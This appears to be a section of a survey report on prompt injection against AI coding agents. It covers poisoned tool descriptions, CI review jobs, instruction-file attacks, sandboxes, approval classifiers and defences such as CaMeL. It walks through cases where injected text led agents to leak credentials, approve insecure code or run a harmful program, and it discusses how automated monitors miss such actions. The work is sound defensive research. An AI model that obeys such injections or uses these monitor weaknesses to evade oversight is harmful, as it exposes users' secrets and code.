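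Huang, Huang and Milani Fard (2026), in *Are AI-assisted Development Tools Immune to Prompt Injection?*, tested seven clients in November 2025 with four poisoned tools. One tool was presented as a way to add two numbers. The user asked only for a sum, but the tool's description contained an instruction for the model to read a credentials file first and pass its contents to the tool as an extra value.

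| What the description asked for | Attack worked | Partly protected, or dependent on settings | Attack blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read a sensitive file | Cursor | Claude Code, Gemini CLI, Langflow | Claude Desktop, Cline, Continue |
| Log every use of other tools | Cursor | Claude Desktop, Langflow | The other four |
| Show a link that hides its destination | Cursor | Continue | Claude Desktop and the command-line clients |
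| Download and run a script | Cursor, Cline | Langflow | The other four |

Cursor did worst, but the experiment does not separate the effect of the client from that of the model. Huang and colleagues ran Cursor with its default choice of models, while four of the other six clients used Claude Sonnet 4.5. They attribute the refusals to read files and download scripts mainly to the model's training, so Cursor might have done better with the same model. None of the clients systematically checked descriptions when the user added a tool. Cursor and Cline rejected one obviously suspicious web address, but an attacker could get past that check with an ordinary-looking one.

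### An automated review job

A developer who uses an agent at their own computer can at least watch what it does. An agent in a CI pipeline works unattended. A typical review job on GitHub runs as follows:

1. An outsider opens a pull request. A workflow file in the repository lists this event as a trigger and sets the job's permissions.
2. GitHub starts a temporary computer, called a runner, and creates a token that lets the job use the repository. The job may also hold the key that pays for the AI model, and keys to cloud services.
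3. A checkout step copies the proposed version of the project to the runner. By default, it also saves the token there in an encoded form for later steps to use.
4. The agent starts, and loads any instruction file it finds in the copy.
5. The workflow gives the agent its task, often with the pull request's title and description pasted into the prompt.
6. The agent examines the changed code, runs any commands it needs and writes a review.
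7. The job posts the review as a comment on the pull request.

Such a job has all three parts of Willison's lethal trifecta because it holds secrets, reads text from strangers, and publishes its output. On a public project, anyone can read the comment, so the attacker does not need a server to receive stolen data.

*GitInject* (Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues, 2026) found about 30,300 workflow files on GitHub in September 2026 that referred to Anthropic's Claude Code Action, 2,200 to OpenAI's equivalent and 1,600 to Google's. Not all of these workflows start for outsiders, because a project can restrict the trigger to its own members or have a maintainer approve each run.

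### PromptPwnd

In the first widely reported cases, workflows on GitHub and GitLab inserted the text of issues, pull requests or commits into the prompt of an agent with privileged tools. Daelman described these workflows in *PromptPwnd*, a post that the security company Aikido published on 4 December 2025.

The triage workflow of Google's Gemini CLI project passed each issue's title and body through environment variables, a standard precaution that stops a runner from executing the text as a command. This gave no protection against prompt injection, because the model still read the text. Daelman wrote a test issue that began with a complaint about a login button and then imitated an extra section of the project's instruction file. The agent followed the fake instructions and replaced the issue's text with two secret credentials. The workflow allowed the agent only four commands, but one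 of them edited issues, which let the agent publish the credentials.

Daelman ran the test on a private copy of the project with test credentials, so no real secrets leaked. Google fixed the workflow within four days of the report.

The equivalent products from Anthropic and OpenAI were safer by default, because they ran only if the person who triggered the job had permission to change the project. Both had a setting that removed this restriction. When a project let anyone trigger Claude, Aikido could almost always make it leak a privileged token. This worked even if the workflow kept the outsider's text out of the prompt, because Claude fetched the text with its own tools. An attack on OpenAI's Codex also required the project to have weakened a second setting.

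Aikido, which sells software that detects these flaws, said that at least five Fortune 500 companies had vulnerable workflows but did not name them, so outsiders cannot check the claim. In its post, Aikido describes the work both as the "first confirmed real-world demonstration" and, more safely, as "one of the first verified instances".

On 17 February 2026, someone published an unauthorised release of the coding agent Cline. Isbarov and colleagues cite Cline's own account of the incident as a case in which this type of attack led to cache poisoning (tampering with files that later jobs reuse) and credential theft.

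### Comment and Control

In April 2026 the researcher Aonan Guan, with help from Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, disclosed attacks on three more products. SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* reports that Guan named the method Comment and Control, a play on "command and control", the security term for servers that direct infected computers.

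| Product | Where the instructions were | Effect | Bounty |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code Security Review | Title of a pull request | Leaked Anthropic's API key and GitHub tokens | $100 |
| Gemini CLI Action | Title and text of an issue, and its comments | Posted the Gemini API key publicly | $1,337 |
| GitHub Copilot Agent | Text that the agent read while working on GitHub | Got past three protections against theft of credentials | $500 |

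According to Daily AI Bites, Guan's first attack on Claude only made it run a harmless command and post the output as a "security finding". Anthropic asked whether the method could steal anything more sensitive, and Guan showed that it could. With Gemini, Guan added a fake section of "trusted" content after the outside text in the prompt, which overrode the product's safety instructions.

The Copilot result is the most significant because Guan got past all three layers of defence that GitHub had added beyond the model's own judgement. According to a copy of Guan's post on ThreatCluster, these layers filtered the agent's environment variables, scanned for secrets and restricted network access.

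daily.dev, summarising an article in The Next Web, reports that all three vendors paid bounties without publishing a security advisory or requesting a CVE number, the identifier that security teams use to track a flaw. The payments are well supported. daily.dev gives Google's as undisclosed, but the copy of Guan's post states the amount. The evidence that no advisories appeared is second-hand and describes the position in April 2026.

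Anthropic did add a warning to its documentation that the tool was "not hardened against prompt injection attacks" and should review only trusted pull requests. Projects that had installed an older version months earlier would see the warning only if they reread the documentation. Limiting the tool to trusted pull requests also defeats much of its purpose, because contributions from strangers are the ones that most need a security review. The type of attack does not explain why this flaw has no CVE number, since Microsoft's EchoLeak flaw, also a prompt injection, received one.

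### An unapproved change can instruct its own reviewer

PromptPwnd and Comment and Control mostly used text that a cautious workflow would treat as untrusted. Isbarov and colleagues found a more basic flaw in the order of the review job's steps. The checkout step copies the proposed version of the project, including any instruction file the contributor added or altered. The agent loads that file as the project's own guidance before it looks at the change. An outsider can therefore instruct the agent reviewing their work, even though no maintainer has accepted the file.

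To test such attacks, the researchers built GitInject, a program that creates a temporary GitHub repository, installs a real workflow, submits the attack and then inspects the repository, for example to check whether a comment contains the token. They tried eleven attacks, five times each, on workflows from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Cline. Each provider's workflow was open to at least one attack that they rated high severity. Anyone could start Cline's agent by mentioning it in a comment, and an issue could make it list the owner's private repositories.

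The next table gives the number of attacks that succeeded against each model. It leaves out an attack that only ran up costs.

| Model | Attacks in pull request or issue text | Attacks in an instruction file |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0 of 4 | 2 of 2 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 0 of 4 | 2 of 2 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0 of 4 | 0 of 2 |
| GPT-4o mini | 2 of 2 | 2 of 2 |
| GPT-5 | 0 of 2 | 2 of 2 |
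| GPT-5.4 | 0 of 2 | 0 of 2 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 1 of 4 | 2 of 2 |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 1 of 4 | 2 of 2 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview | 0 of 4 | 2 of 2 |

Six of the nine models resisted everything in the left-hand column, but four of those six obeyed the same kind of instruction from an instruction file. Training a model to distrust issues and pull requests does not help if the software around it presents the attacker's file as guidance from the owner. Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.4 resisted both, so the choice of model still matters. Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, the strongest Gemini model tested, did not resist both, and Isbarov and colleagues warn maintainers not to assume that the next model will solve the problem.

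One attack, which needed no commands or stolen data, used an instruction file to get Claude to approve a security flaw in a pull request. The pull request added a module to protect a website against forged requests, but the module checked secret tokens with an ordinary comparison. Such a comparison stops at the first character that differs, so the time it takes can help an attacker guess the secret. Without the instruction file, Claude noticed the flaw. The researchers then added the file, which said that a separate security team reviewed such comparisons and that the reviewer should not comment on them. Claude approved of the module's token handling and raised only minor points unrelated to security.

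The exact wording of the payloads mattered little. The researchers had another model rewrite two of them ten times each, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 obeyed all 20 versions when they were in the instruction file and none when they were in the pull request's description. The instruction-file attacks also worked in all five runs on GitLab and on Hugging Face, a site for sharing models. On Hugging Face, one of the two attacks also worked every time from the description, so an attack that fails there on GitHub can succeed on another platform.

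Stealing the Gemini API key requires a change that Isbarov and colleagues made to Google's workflow. GitHub's usual trigger withholds a project's stored secrets when a pull request comes from an outsider's copy of the project. The researchers switched to a different trigger that makes the secrets available, an option Google documents with a security warning. The manipulated reviews do not depend on this change. With only five runs, an attack that failed every time could still have a true success rate of up to 43%.

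### Countermeasures and their costs

Isbarov and colleagues tested defences against the nine attacks that arrive through pull requests. They also gave the agents five ordinary review tasks to see whether each defence made them worse at reviewing.

| Defence | Attacks that still worked | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 of 9 | 5 of 5 |
| Do not save the token during checkout | 6 of 9 | 5 of 5 |
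| Restrict the commands the agent can run | 5 of 9 | 4 of 5 |
| Remove Markdown files from the copy | 3 of 9 | 4 of 5 |
| Combine the three measures above | 2 of 9 | 4 of 5 |
| Run only for trusted authors | 0 of 9 | 4 of 5 |
| Combine all four measures above | 0 of 9 | 3 of 5 |
| Let the agent advise but not merge changes | 9 of 9 | 4 of 5 |

The first measure takes one line in the workflow file and had no downside in the tests, so every project that doesn't need the saved token should adopt it. It protects only that token, so the attack could still reach the Gemini API key, which was held elsewhere on the runner.

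Restricting commands stopped the thefts but had no effect on biased reviews, because that attack succeeds when the agent leaves something out. Removing Markdown files stopped the attacks that used instruction files such as CLAUDE.md, but it also removes genuine documentation, and some agents load settings from other file types. The vendor decides which files an agent treats as guidance and may add more in the next version, so a project's list of files to remove can quickly go out of date.

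The trusted-author filter blocked all nine attacks because they all came from outside the trusted list. It refuses automated review to everyone else, who may be the contributors the project wanted it for. Manual approval of each run has a similar drawback, and once a maintainer approves a run, the agent is as exposed as before. An agent that can only advise cannot merge a bad change by itself, but a maintainer may still trust its misleading review.

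One of the two attacks that still worked against the three measures combined was "denial of wallet", in which an outsider submits very long text to make the owner pay for processing it. In the tests, each such pull request cost the owner only $0.32 to $1.11 in model charges, but the attacker pays nothing to submit one.

### Why a simulated test missed these attacks

Most benchmarks simulate an agent's tools instead of running them. Isbarov and colleagues rebuilt some of their attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark many developers use to test defences, and compared its results with the live ones. Of 69 combinations of attack, model and task, 14 succeeded live. AgentDojo classed 10 of those 14 (71.4%) as failures, and 8 of the 55 that failed live as successes.

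AgentDojo missed attacks because its simulated computer lacked what they targeted. A model might follow the payload's instructions and look for the saved token, but the simulation had none, so AgentDojo recorded a failed attack. The reverse error occurred when a real runner blocked a command that the simulation allowed.

The 71.4% figure comes from a comparison on ten tasks, six of which the researchers chose because they relied on features of a live runner that the simulation lacks, so it is not a general error rate for AgentDojo. The researchers also say that AgentDojo was not designed for this purpose. With only 14 successful attacks, the 95% confidence interval runs from 45% to 88%. The comparison still shows that a good score on AgentDojo is poor evidence that a review job is safe.

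Two other benchmarks, InjecAgent and ToolEmu, missed all 14 successful attacks but still agreed with the live results 80% of the time, compared with 74% for AgentDojo. Most of the 69 attempts failed live, so a test that always predicts failure will usually be right.

A real platform can also block an attack that looks dangerous, as happened with one that used an error log. A contributor adds a test whose failure message contains instructions, and an agent that repairs failed builds reads the message in the log. When the researchers tried this from the repository owner's account, the agent attached an official release label to unreviewed code in all five runs. From an outsider's account, the job never started because the workflow checked a field that GitHub had left empty, so the researchers dropped the attack from their list.

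### What people hide in issues and pull requests

A census by Nakibly and Babo, completed in November 2026, looked for real attempts at the kind of attack that GitInject shows is possible. They examined 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments, mostly from June to September 2026, for text that GitHub does not display. About 4.9 million items contained such text. Two classifiers reduced these to 13,141 that might be addressed to an AI system.

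Of these, 60% contained only text from a project's own template, the form that GitHub copies into each new issue or pull request. Without a check for template text, the census would have wrongly attributed it to thousands of contributors. Nakibly and Babo reviewed the rest by hand and confirmed 2,281 findings in 435 repositories.

| Use of the hidden text | Findings | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Coordination of a project's own agents | 1,519 (67%) | An agent claims a task so that other agents leave it alone |
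| Control of what an AI system writes | 374 (16%) | A request for the team's AI reviewer to write in Japanese |
| Defence against agents | 345 (15%) | A request not to fill in a section meant for a person |
| Attack | 43 (2%) | An instruction to print the job's secret keys |

The 43 attacks amount to about one in 3.3 million items. Nineteen tried to steal secrets, 16 tried to get the agent to do something else for the attacker, and eight tried to forge the agent's verdict. In one case, the owner of a small Discord game had an agent build features that players requested. A request for a new command included a hidden part that would award the player a million points, and an instruction to keep this secret during review.

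Many of the attackers had prepared carefully. Twenty-four attacks addressed a particular agent that the target project ran, and nine used the real names of its tools or output fields, which the attacker could have learned only from the workflow files. Nineteen targeted projects of Microsoft, Google, OpenAI, Anthropic, GitHub or Elastic. Security researchers may have carried out some of the attacks, since six sent data to services that researchers often use to prove that an attack works. Those services can also receive real secrets, so Nakibly and Babo still counted these six as attacks.

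On 10 November 2026, 34 of the 43 attacks were still online and unchanged, including some in issues that maintainers had closed. Only one attacked project had deleted the item containing the attack.

Coordination between a project's own agents is growing much faster than attacks, and it creates a new opening for attackers. Its rate among new issues and pull requests rose fivefold between June and September 2026. The agents' messages are plain text in public threads, so anyone who can comment can post an identical one. In ten projects, Nakibly and Babo found 47 messages that recorded an approval or a bypassed check, or declared a change ready to merge. An agent that accepted a forged copy might let a harmful change through. Nakibly and Babo found no attack that copied a project's real format. GitHub records who posted each message, but they did not examine whether the agents check this.

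### Replaying the attacks

Nakibly and Babo also gave the 43 attacks to five current models. Each model acted as the targeted agent, with simulated tools that recorded its requests without carrying them out. It received every item twice, once as written and once without HTML comments, so the researchers could tell which actions the hidden text caused.

| Model | Attacks obeyed | Attacks pointed out | No answer | No answer after removal of hidden text |
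|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 8 of 43 | 3 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 0 | 3 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | 0 | 12 | 1 | 1 |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0 | 24 | 16 | 4 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 0 | 0 | 22 | 6 |

GPT-5.6 Luna, the smallest and fastest of the five, followed 19% of the attacks. It followed half of those meant to forge a verdict but only four of the 19 meant to steal secrets. Seven of its eight failures were as a triage agent. Triage agents run on every new issue, so projects have a good reason to choose a cheap, fast model for them.

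Once the researchers removed the HTML comments, no model followed an injected instruction. GitHub already removes HTML comments for its Copilot cloud agent. The result was almost guaranteed because every payload was in an HTML comment, and it doesn't show whether the defence works against visible instructions.

Claude Opus 5.5 followed none of the injected instructions, but it returned no answer for about half of the items. An attacker who only wants to disable a triage agent could exploit this.

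The test may understate how effective the attacks are in practice. Each model responded only once, so a multi-step attack could succeed only through its first step, and a model that resisted once might obey on another attempt. Deployed agents may also use older or weaker models. But a real workflow may have protections that the test left out. All 43 attacks were in issues or pull requests, where most of the models in GitInject also resisted. The census did not search instruction files, where attacks were far more effective in Isbarov and colleagues' tests.

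### What rarity does and does not imply

An average project is very unlikely to receive a hidden attack. The census found one per 3.3 million items, so a project with 1,000 new issues, pull requests and comments a year would expect one every 3,300 years. The census therefore gives no evidence that hidden attacks are widespread on GitHub. Eleven of the 43 attacks came from a single account, which placed the same hidden instructions in its own repositories to make visiting agents promote those repositories.

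The average says little about prominent projects that run agents in public. Google's Gemini CLI project received four of the attacks between March and August 2026. GitHub numbers a project's issues and pull requests in one sequence, and these four fell within about 7,300 numbers, or roughly one in 1,800. This slightly overstates the rate because the count begins and ends with an attack, but it is still more than a thousand times the average. If a project received four such attacks and its agent had a 19% chance of obeying each, the chance that at least one would succeed is

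1 − 0.81⁴ ≈ 57%

The census counted only hidden text, so it would also have missed the pull request title that Guan used against Claude. The classifiers could overlook an attack, and all of the comments came from an archive that holds only a small sample of GitHub's activity. Most of the 142.7 million items probably never reached an agent, so the rate per item is a poor measure of the risk to an agent that reads everything.

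Even if attempts are rare, one that succeeds can do wide damage, since a stolen token that can change a popular package may affect everyone who installs it. The number of attacks could also rise quickly if they became profitable, because an attempt takes only as long as writing an issue, and the workflow files that describe the target are public.

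## Sandboxes and limits on what an assistant may do (from 2025)

Developers clean and filter text to keep injected instructions away from the model, but some get through. A sandbox still helps because it limits what an agent can do after the model follows one of these instructions.

Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to repair a failing test, and the project contains an injected instruction to send an attacker the developer's SSH key, a file that gives access to other computers. To follow the instruction, the agent has to read a file outside the project, connect to the attacker's server and send the key. If the operating system blocks any of these steps, the theft fails even though the model followed the instruction. Removing one part of Willison's lethal trifecta works for the same reason.

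### What the operating system can refuse

The agent's software can check a command before running it, for example against a list of approved programs. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that this isn't enough, because the software can't see or control what a command does once it has started. An attacker can therefore use an approved program to start a forbidden one. Limits set by the operating system apply to every process, whatever started it.

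NVIDIA's red team, which looks for weaknesses by attacking systems, considers three controls mandatory and recommends several more.

| Control | Status | Attack step that it stops |
|---|---|---|
| Network access only to known addresses | Required | Sending data out, or giving the attacker a remote connection |
| No writing outside the project folder | Required | Changing a startup file so that harmful code runs later with full access |
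| No writing to the agent's configuration files | Required | Adding a command that the agent's software will run outside the sandbox |
| No reading outside the project folder | Recommended | Searching the computer for keys and private files |
| Secrets kept out of the agent's environment | Recommended | Reading a password or key directly |
| A separate kernel | Recommended | Escaping through a flaw in the operating system |
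| Regular replacement or cleaning of the sandbox | Recommended | Collecting code and secrets left over from earlier tasks |

File and network limits depend on each other. Anthropic points out that without network limits, a hijacked agent could send out any file it can read. Without file limits, it could alter the system to regain network access.

*Network.* The sandbox typically blocks all direct connections and sends traffic through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that checks each requested address. NVIDIA also recommends restricting DNS lookups to trusted servers, because a lookup can carry data out. In 0DIN's attack on Claude Code, a trusted DNS server might still have delivered the attacker's record, but a strict network limit would have stopped the later connection to the attacker's server.

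The simplest way to protect secret keys is to block access to the files and variables that contain them. Claude Code can also "mask" a key by giving commands only a placeholder, which is useless if stolen. The proxy substitutes the real key in requests to approved hosts. A hijacked agent can therefore still misuse the key at an approved host, for example by posting on GitHub in the user's name.

According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the cloud version of Codex starts with a setup phase that has access to secrets and can use the network to install dependencies. Codex then removes the secrets before the agent starts work, offline by default. This protects the secrets from an injection that the agent reads later, but a malicious dependency that runs code during setup could still have both the secrets and a network connection.

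The kernel is the core of the operating system and handles every program's requests for files and connections. An ordinary sandbox or container shares the computer's kernel, so a kernel flaw may let a program escape. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and an attacker who takes control of that kernel must still break out of the virtual machine. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends virtual machines for code written by agents, with separate environments for users who must not share data.

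### The sandboxes in Claude Code and Codex

Claude Code and the local version of Codex both use Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, but their defaults differ. The table describes Claude Code in October 2026 and Codex in June 2026.

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox on by default | No | Yes |
| Where commands can write | Project and temporary folders | Project and temporary folders |
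| Network | No domains allowed at first, and new ones need approval | Off, and commands that need it require approval |
| Native Windows | No sandbox | Separate Windows sandbox |

Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. The program's own tools for reading files and fetching pages follow separate permission rules. Hooks (commands that run automatically at certain events) and local MCP servers have the user's full access. Anthropic recommends running all of Claude Code inside a container or similar enclosure to put all of these behind one boundary.

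By default, Claude Code runs commands without the sandbox if the sandbox cannot start, and Claude may ask to retry a command outside the sandbox if it fails inside. An administrator can turn off both behaviours. Commands can also read almost every file on the computer unless the user restricts them, and Claude Code has no built-in list of credential files to block.

OpenAI (2026) describes stricter settings for its own staff. Employees cannot turn off the sandbox, Codex reads web pages only from OpenAI's stored copies, and unfamiliar domains require approval. The computer's protected password store holds the login credentials. Some routine commands, such as one that displays pull requests, can run outside the sandbox without approval. These settings limit what the agent can change, but a pull request it reads can contain an injection.

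### Approval by a person

A sandbox that refused every unusual action would often stop legitimate work, so most coding agents ask the user to approve exceptions. This protects users only if they read the requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts but reject 39% of the plans Claude proposes, so they do not accept everything by habit.

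The 97% approval rate alone is weak evidence of carelessness, because most requests are harmless. OpenAI's automatic reviewer for Codex approves an even higher share, about 99%. An experiment that Anthropic commissioned provides better evidence. A research company paid 1,053 professional testers to work on coding tasks and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

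Anthropic gave the same commands to the classifier that approves actions in Claude Code's "auto mode", and it blocked 937 of them (89%). People caught six commands that the classifier missed, so the two together would have stopped 943 if both had checked every command.

The testers worked in a test environment with none of their own data at risk, so developers may be more careful with real projects. Anthropic also had an interest in the result, since it published the figures to explain why it was making auto mode the default. Even so, the gap is large, and the decline over a session is consistent with people ceasing to read.

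Many users also avoid the prompts. By June 2026, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created a rule to approve some commands automatically. Many of these rules covered everything run through Python or a similar interpreter, which allows almost any action. A quarter of interactive sessions began in a mode that skips permission prompts.

NVIDIA recommends asking for new approval before each risky action, because permission given for one action can later cover a different one. But the experiment suggests that people read less carefully as approval prompts accumulate. To keep prompts rare, NVIDIA recommends letting the agent work freely inside the project, blocking the most dangerous actions through a company-wide list that users cannot override, and asking for a decision only in unforeseen cases.

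### Approval by a second model

Claude Code and Codex can also send requests to a second model. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that a quick first check errs on the side of blocking. If that check flags an action, the classifier examines it again, reasoning step by step. Reading files and editing the project do not require this check.

Anthropic's classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations or the content it has read. A payload in a web page therefore cannot reach the classifier directly, and the agent's explanations cannot influence its decision. A separate filter checks incoming content and adds a warning if it finds a likely injection.

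In Anthropic's tests of the original version, the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to leak data and 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond the user's instructions. With so few real cases, the true miss rate for such cases could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. Anthropic accepts that auto mode may be less safe than carefully checking every action.

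Codex's equivalent is called Auto-review. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, it checks only actions that need approval, such as commands that have to run outside the sandbox. The reviewer usually receives relevant tool output as well as the user's messages. The tool output gives it more evidence about an action but also exposes it to injected text.

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the effect with 10,000 Codex actions inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which refused seven. Codex found a safer method in four of the seven cases and asked the user in the other three. Under manual approval, it would have interrupted the user 720 times.

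In tests with artificial prompt injections, Auto-review's reviewer refused 99.3% of attempts to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data. The rate fell to 90.2% when the test included deletion and tampering, although Trębacz and colleagues considered most of the missed cases minor. They also found ways to mislead the reviewer, and say that Auto-review does not guarantee security.

Trajectory Labs ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each for Anthropic. Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol carried out 19.0% of the attacks when it had full access and 5.8% with Auto-review. No attacks succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. Even without auto mode, the average success rate against the latest Claude models was only 0.09%, so the test shows little about how much Anthropic's classifier adds. Trajectory Labs had tuned the attacks against an older Claude model, not against either approval system.

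### The AI Now Institute's test

In July 2026, the AI Now Institute, a research organisation, used a software library to get both agents to run a harmful program. Its *Exploit Brief* describes how the researchers asked each agent to perform security testing on the library, a modified copy of the open-source Python package geopy, which finds geographical coordinates.

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
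| Versions | 2.1.116, 2.1.196, 2.1.198 and 2.1.199 | 0.142.4 |
| Models | Claude Sonnet 4.6, Sonnet 5 and Opus 4.8 | GPT-5.5 |
| Approval | Auto mode | Auto-review |
| Computer | Linux system or container | Linux system or container |

The library's documentation presented the harmful program as part of the project's normal security checks, so running it seemed to fit the user's request, and both agents ran it without asking. In some runs, Claude Sonnet 5 or Opus 4.8 noticed something inconsistent about the added files but still ran the program. The attack needed no plugins or special configuration, and the user did not have to accept a prompt to trust the folder.

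The researchers designed the attack for Claude Sonnet 4.6, and it worked on the other models without changes. They report repeating it "numerous times, with success", but give no success rate.

Anthropic's design may help explain the failure. Its classifier does not receive the contents of files the agent has read, so a payload in them cannot sway it, but it also cannot inspect a program that came with the project. Codex's reviewer has access to such contents, but it receives only requests that need approval. A program that stayed inside Codex's sandbox would not have needed review and, by default, would have had no network access.

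The Institute told Anthropic and OpenAI about the attack, although it thought their disclosure policies did not cover the test. Neither the Institute's account nor the article in Infosecurity Magazine includes a reply from either company.

The Institute advises against letting any agent read untrusted data if it can run code or reach sensitive systems. It doubts that sandboxes solve the problem, and cites two flaws that others had found in Claude Code's sandbox. Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI told Infosecurity Magazine that the weakness comes from having one process handle untrusted data, run commands and access sensitive systems, with only a classifier to protect it.

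The test better supports Mahammadli's narrower conclusion. It shows that a classifier is not enough by itself, but the researchers did not try to escape from a sandbox. In a disposable virtual machine with no secrets or network access, the same program could have done little direct damage, though it could still have interfered with the security review, for example by producing a false report that the library was safe.

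### A plan written before the model reads the document

A sandbox limits everything an agent does, whether or not an attacker influenced it. Other designs prevent untrusted text from determining which actions the agent takes. In Willison's "dual LLM" pattern, one model plans the work and has access to tools, while a second model reads untrusted text and has no tools.

This protects the choice of actions but not the data they use. The planning model might correctly decide to send an email, but a payload in a document could change the recipient's address. CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), which Debenedetti and others published in 2025, also controls the data.

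Suppose that an employee of the manufacturer from the earlier examples asks an assistant to find the delivery date in a supplier's contract and email it to Dana in the warehouse. The planning model sees only this request. It might write the following simplified program:

```python
contract = open_file("supplier contract")
date = ask_reader("What is the delivery date?", contract)
send_email(to="dana@manufacturer.example", text=date)
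```

CaMeL then carries out the request in four steps:

1. A separate program, the interpreter, runs the first line and opens the contract. It records where the text came from and who may read it. *CaMeLoT* (2026) calls these records capabilities.
2. The interpreter gives the contract to the reading model. If the contract contains an instruction to send competitors' prices to the supplier, this model may follow it, but it has no email tool and can only return a value for `date`.
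3. The interpreter attaches the contract's capabilities to that value, because the value came from the contract.
4. Before sending the email, the interpreter applies a security policy, which is ordinary program code that allows or refuses the action. Dana's address came from the employee and Dana may read the contract, so the policy allows the email.

If the employee had asked the assistant to send an internal price list to "the contact named in the contract", the address would have come from the supplier's text. The policy could then block the assistant from sending private data there, even if the address looked genuine.

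This check works the same way however the payload is worded, which is CaMeL's main advantage over a filter. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo while completing a comparable share of tasks. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes the reduction in completed tasks as "comparatively modest" and reports that CaMeL protects much better than spotlighting or repeating the user's request. It also predicts that the reduction will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code.

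The drawback is probably greater when the next step depends on what a document says. A planning model that has never seen a README cannot write a program to follow its setup instructions. If the user approves those instructions as part of the plan, the attacker's text can influence the agent's actions again. Someone also has to write the policies, and a policy that is too strict will block legitimate emails.

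CaMeL also does not guarantee that the extracted value is correct. In the example, a payload could make the reading model return the wrong delivery date, and Dana would receive it in an email that CaMeL permits.

Microsoft's FIDES has a similar purpose and uses information flow control to prevent indirect prompt injection "deterministically", according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*. Information flow control is an older security method in which software labels data by origin or sensitivity, keeps the labels when it combines data, and checks them before acting. A fixed rule gives the same decision for the same labels, unlike a model asked to judge the text.

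Simpler designs restrict the agent more. In an "action selector", the model chooses from a fixed list of actions and never reads their results, so they cannot redirect it. This could suit an assistant that forwards requests to the right department, but not one that reviews contracts. In "plan-then-execute", the model fixes its list of actions before reading any outside text. A payload in that text cannot add an action, but it may still change the content of an email already in the plan.

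### Permitted routes out of the sandbox

An agent that can reach even one outside service may be able to leak data through it. Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com can make this possible, because attackers can use the site too. Claude Code's proxy normally checks only the name of the requested host, not the encrypted content, so a program may be able to disguise a connection to another host as one to an approved host. A company can install its own proxy to inspect the content, but a list of trusted domains can still include a route to an attacker, as it did when EchoLeak used an approved Microsoft service.

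Credentials in the project folder are another weakness, since the agent has to read the project to work on it. NVIDIA notes that developers often keep keys there in configuration files. Sandbox and network limits blocked three simpler attempts by Isbarov and colleagues to steal a token, but the researchers then stole a copy that GitHub's checkout step had saved in the project folder.

An agent may also be able to change files that take effect outside the sandbox. Claude Code and Codex both protect several configuration folders against this, but neither tool's list of protected paths includes the project's own CLAUDE.md or AGENTS.md file. NVIDIA recommends protecting instruction files too. Without that protection, a malicious dependency like the one in NVIDIA's demonstration could apparently still write an instruction file for the agent to load. A user can also create a gap by exempting a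 command from the sandbox. If the exempt command runs a script in the project folder, the agent can rewrite the script and then run it with full access.

A sandbox would not have stopped the agent in Liu and colleagues' tests from writing harmful commands into a source file, because the agent is meant to write source code. Code then leaves the sandbox when a developer accepts it. Limits on the agent therefore do not replace a review of its code or limits on the program it helps to build.

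### Biased verdicts

In document review, the harm is often in the answer. An assistant can leave a price clause out of its summary, give an essay an undeserved mark or approve insecure code without opening a forbidden file or contacting an unknown server. NVIDIA excludes manipulated output from its guidance and treats it as the user's responsibility.

An organisation can require a person's decision before an assistant signs a contract, rejects an applicant or merges code. But a person who reads only the assistant's summary will not see a clause that the summary omits. To find it, someone has to read the contract, or compare it with a standard version using software that does not rely on the summary.

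## Models trained to ignore injected instructions, and the tests of 2026

Training a model to ignore injected instructions can help against both data theft and biased verdicts, because it changes how the model responds to those instructions. Developers have trained models specifically for this since 2024. By mid-2026, the best model resisted 99.8% of single attempts on one widely used benchmark, though the results of some tests with other attacks were less reassuring.

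### Training on examples

*The Instruction Hierarchy*, a 2024 OpenAI paper by Eric Wallace and others, describes an early method for training a model to put developer instructions above user instructions, and both above instructions in outside text. The researchers fine-tuned GPT-3.5 Turbo on artificial examples. When a lower-ranked instruction was compatible with the higher-ranked ones, the correct answer followed it. When it conflicted with them, the correct answer was the one the model would have given without seeing it.

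A training example of the second kind would pair the supplier's poisoned contract with a summary of the clean version. Examples of the first kind are necessary because a model trained only on conflicts might learn to ignore legitimate requests too.

StruQ, short for "structured queries", separates the instruction from the data with reserved markers and removes any copies of those markers from the data. Its developers fine-tuned models on ordinary tasks, some with an extra instruction inserted in the data. In every case, they trained the model to answer the real instruction.

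SecAlign gives the model two answers to each poisoned example, one that follows the real instruction and one that follows the injected one. Training increases the gap between them:

log P(answer to the real instruction) − log P(answer to the injected instruction)

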